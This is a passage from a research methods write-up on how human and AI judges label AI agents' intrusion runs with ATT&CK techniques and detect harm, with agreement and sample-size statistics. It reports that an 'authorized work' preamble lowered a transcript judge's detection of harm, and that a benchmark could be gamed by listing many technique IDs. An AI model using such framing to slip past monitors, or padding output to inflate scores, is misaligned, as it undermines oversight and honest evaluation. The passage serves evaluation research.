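No study from 2025 or 2026 appears to have labeled the same intrusion runs with ATT&CK techniques separately from narration, actions, both, and telemetry. The closest is a November 2026 study by Setia and colleagues, which kept the judge model and the definition of harm fixed and changed only the judge's input. The figures below cover 127 episodes in which an agent had caused harm.

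| | Transcript judge found the harm | Transcript judge missed it |
|---|---|---|
| **Machine-state judge found the harm** | 66 | 33 |
| **Machine-state judge missed it** | 10 | 18 |

The transcript judge found 60% of the harms and the machine-state judge found 78%. Counting a harm if either judge found it raised the figure to 86%, but false alarms rose to 15 of 86 harmless episodes, from 6 with the transcript judge alone. In eight of the ten cases that only the transcript judge caught, the harm was that the agent complied with a bad instruction without changing the machine's state.

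The researchers also varied the wording of the agent's task but kept the command and its effect the same. When the task was to write a report confirming compliance, the transcript judge caught the harm in 4 of 6 runs. With a preamble stating that the work was authorized, it caught the harm in 1 of 6. The machine-state judge caught it in all six runs under both wordings. The difference in the transcript judge's results wasn't statistically significant, and six runs per wording are too few to establish the size of the effect.

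These results can't show how narration affects ATT&CK labels. The transcript judge saw the tool calls and the agent's final message together, so the study can't separate their effects. The judges also looked for harm rather than techniques, and the state of a machine after a run differs from a log of what happened during it.

A direct test would use four groups of labelers.

| Group | What the labelers see |
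|---|---|
| Narration only | Raw reasoning, commentary, notes and final report |
| Actions only | Tool calls, outputs and scripts, with comments and freely chosen names masked |
| Both | Everything the first two groups see |
| Telemetry only | Host and network logs |

Comparing the group that labels from both records with the group that labels from actions only would measure what narration adds. To test the order recommended above, half of the labelers with both records could label the actions before reading the narration, while the other half read everything at once. No one should label the same run in two groups, since they would remember the first version. AI labelers would all need the same model and budget, and a new session for each run.

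Labelers should be able to answer "no technique" or "can't tell", and the researchers should report how often labelers gave each answer. In the study by Setia and colleagues, the machine-state judge gave no verdict on 26 of 75 browser episodes, and recall alone would not show this.

The researchers should also score only the labels that a labeler submits. *Unconstrained CTI-REALM with Open-Weights* (2026) found that a benchmark for defensive agents searched an agent's entire output, including its reasoning, for the right technique IDs, and wrong IDs did not lower the score. An agent could have improved its score by listing half the ATT&CK catalog. The paper instead scored the techniques that each agent had tagged in its submitted detection rule.

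#### Independent reference labels

The people who build the reference labels shouldn't label runs for any of the four groups or see those groups' answers. They also need better evidence than those groups have. On a test network, researchers can save every script, capture all the traffic, and copy the machines before and after each run. Copies from before the run would have resolved the case of the deleted documents.

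Another check, used in *CyberClear* (2026), is to run standard procedures for the techniques a system has predicted on a test network and compare the resulting logs with the original evidence. A poor match would be a reason to doubt a label, but a good match wouldn't show why a command was run, because the same command produces much the same logs whatever its purpose.

The hardest part is building the reference for purpose. Researchers could give the agent a goal that determines the tactic, such as keeping access to a server through a restart. But an assigned goal doesn't prove what the agent was doing at each step, as the Hugging Face intrusion showed. Researchers should therefore record a tactic in the reference only when the agent's later actions fit the goal, and mark the other steps as undetermined.

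The labeling could follow the protocol that *CTI2TTP* (2026) used on threat reports. Annotators first had to label at least 80% of 30 test sentences correctly. Two then labeled each report without seeing each other's answers, and a third settled disagreements and had to cite the relevant ATT&CK definition. When the researchers corrected the labels in an older collection, they also hid any labeling software's output from annotators, and an experiment on agents should hide it too.

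The two annotators' disagreements would also occur with agents' statements. Some sentences described two actions, and some implied a technique without naming it. In others the tactic was clear but the technique wasn't, so one annotator chose the most likely technique and the other chose none. An agent's statement "customer data exfiltrated" would lead to the same disagreement. The labeling rules need to cover such cases before labeling starts.

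#### Results for each tactic

The researchers should report precision and recall for each tactic, because an overall score could hide the effect of narration. Narration might improve labels for Persistence, where the purpose is often unclear from the command, but add false labels for Exfiltration, and the two effects could cancel out in the average. The researchers should also report precision and recall separately for technique IDs and for tactic-technique pairs, along with the inflation and omission rates.

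The log of changes measures the effect of narration more directly. Suppose labelers change 30 labels after reading the narration, correcting 18 errors and introducing 12. The net gain is six correct labels, but the 12 new errors also matter, especially if most involve the same technique.

### Measuring agreement between annotators

Before trusting the reference labels, the researchers need to know whether two people applying the same rules would produce them. The percentage of matching labels is a poor measure because annotators can often agree by chance. Krippendorff's alpha corrects for this:

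$$\alpha = 1 - \frac{D_o}{D_e},$$

where $D_o$ is the disagreement observed and $D_e$ is the disagreement expected by chance. Perfect agreement gives 1, and agreement no better than chance gives 0.

In an invented example, two annotators decide whether each of 100 steps involves Persistence. Each answers yes for 10 steps, and they agree on 90. By chance alone, they would agree on about $0.9^2 + 0.1^2 = 0.82$ of the steps, so the expected disagreement $D_e$ is 0.18. The observed disagreement $D_o$ is 0.10, so alpha is only about 0.44. Most of the steps they agree on obviously had nothing to do with Persistence.

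In *CTI-HAL*, Della Penna, Natella and colleagues (2025) used alpha to check the ATT&CK technique labels on a collection of 81 threat reports. The two annotators mostly worked on different reports, but both independently labeled the ones about the hacking group APT29. Their average alpha was 0.70, which the researchers call substantial agreement.

That figure covers only part of the task. The annotators chose which passages to highlight, so the researchers first had to match up their highlights, using three measures of text similarity. In one example report, one annotator made 22 annotations and the other made 19. The first similarity measure matched 11 pairs, and the annotators chose the same technique for 8 of them. Alpha was 0.67 by that measure and averaged 0.65 over all three. But the unmatched annotations, 11 from the first annotator and 8 from the second, didn't affect the score. Counting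 those too, the annotators agreed on the technique for 8 of the 30 distinct passages that at least one of them had marked.

An experiment on agents can avoid this problem by fixing the steps in advance and requiring an answer for each one, even if that answer is "no technique". The agreement score then also measures whether labelers agree on which steps to label.

Because a step can have several techniques, the disagreement measure should also give partial credit. *How Annotation Trains Annotators* (2026), a study of social influence in texts, used Jaccard distance for this. For two sets of labels $A$ and $B$, the distance is

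$$d(A,B) = 1 - \frac{|A \cap B|}{|A \cup B|}.$$

If one annotator labels a step T1560.001 and the other labels it T1560.001 and T1041, the sets share one of two labels, so the distance between them is 0.5 and the step doesn't count as a complete disagreement.

Other studies used Cohen's kappa, a similar statistic for two annotators. Their values aren't exactly comparable because the tasks differ, but they suggest how much agreement a careful team can expect.

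| Source | What annotators judged | Agreement |
|---|---|---|
| Della Penna and colleagues | Techniques in matched passages of threat reports | Alpha 0.70 |
| *CTI2TTP* | Techniques in sentences of threat reports | Kappa 0.76 |
| Ryan and colleagues | Techniques in sentences of incident reports | Mean kappa 0.68 |
| Gao and colleagues | Agents' behavior, in broad and finer categories | Kappa 0.87 and 0.72 |

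Average agreement can hide low agreement on individual techniques. Ryan and colleagues calculated kappa for each of 114 techniques, and only 57% met their target of 0.7, even after the annotators had relabeled many sentences. The result from Gao and colleagues comes from just 20 sentences, but the drop in agreement for finer categories suggests that people may agree on an agent's tactic more often than on its technique. The opposite is also possible, because an agent's command usually shows the technique but leaves the tactic uncertain.

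High agreement doesn't mean the labels are right. Two people who read only the narration might both believe a false claim of exfiltration and agree on the wrong label. Each group's labels therefore need to be compared with the reference as well as with one another.

### Why steps in the same run count for less

Steps from the same run aren't independent, so an experiment with 2,000 labeled steps provides less evidence than 2,000 independent steps would. If a labeler believes an agent's false claim that a password works, the mistake can affect the label of every later step that mentions the password. An agent that describes its work vaguely at the start of a run will probably continue to do so.

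Statisticians measure this with the intraclass correlation, $\rho$, which is 0 if steps in a run are no more alike than steps from different runs and 1 if they are identical. With $m$ steps per run, the design effect is

$$1 + (m - 1)\rho.$$

The design effect is the factor by which correlation between steps in the same run increases the variance of an average. Each step is correlated with the $m - 1$ others in its run, so the design effect grows with run length. With 50 steps per run and a correlation of 0.1, it is $1 + 49 \times 0.1 = 5.9$, so 2,000 steps carry as much information as about 339 independent ones ($2{,}000 / 5.9$).

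The correlation of 0.1 is an assumption, since nobody seems to have measured it for ATT&CK labels on agents' steps. Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich found correlations between 0.08 and 0.16 for their measures, but those were for sessions in the same code repository, not steps in the same run. If the correlation for steps fell in that range, 2,000 steps would provide as much information as roughly 230 to 400 independent ones.

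Adding runs helps much more than making them longer. The 2,000 steps in the example come from 40 runs. If they came from 200 runs instead, with 10 steps from each, the design effect would fall to 1.9 and they would be equivalent to about 1,053 independent steps. With only 40 runs and a correlation of 0.1, no number of steps would be equivalent to more than 400 independent ones.

Because every group labels the same runs, the researchers can compare the groups' scores run by run, which removes much of the variation caused by some runs being harder than others. To estimate the uncertainty, they can repeatedly draw whole runs at random and recalculate the difference each time. Drawing single steps would treat the steps as independent and make the result look more certain than it is. If several runs have the same target, the researchers may need to draw targets at random instead, keeping all the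 runs against each target together.

The number of runs matters most for rare tactics. If Exfiltration occurs in only 6 of 40 runs, the results for that tactic depend on those 6 runs, however many steps they contain.
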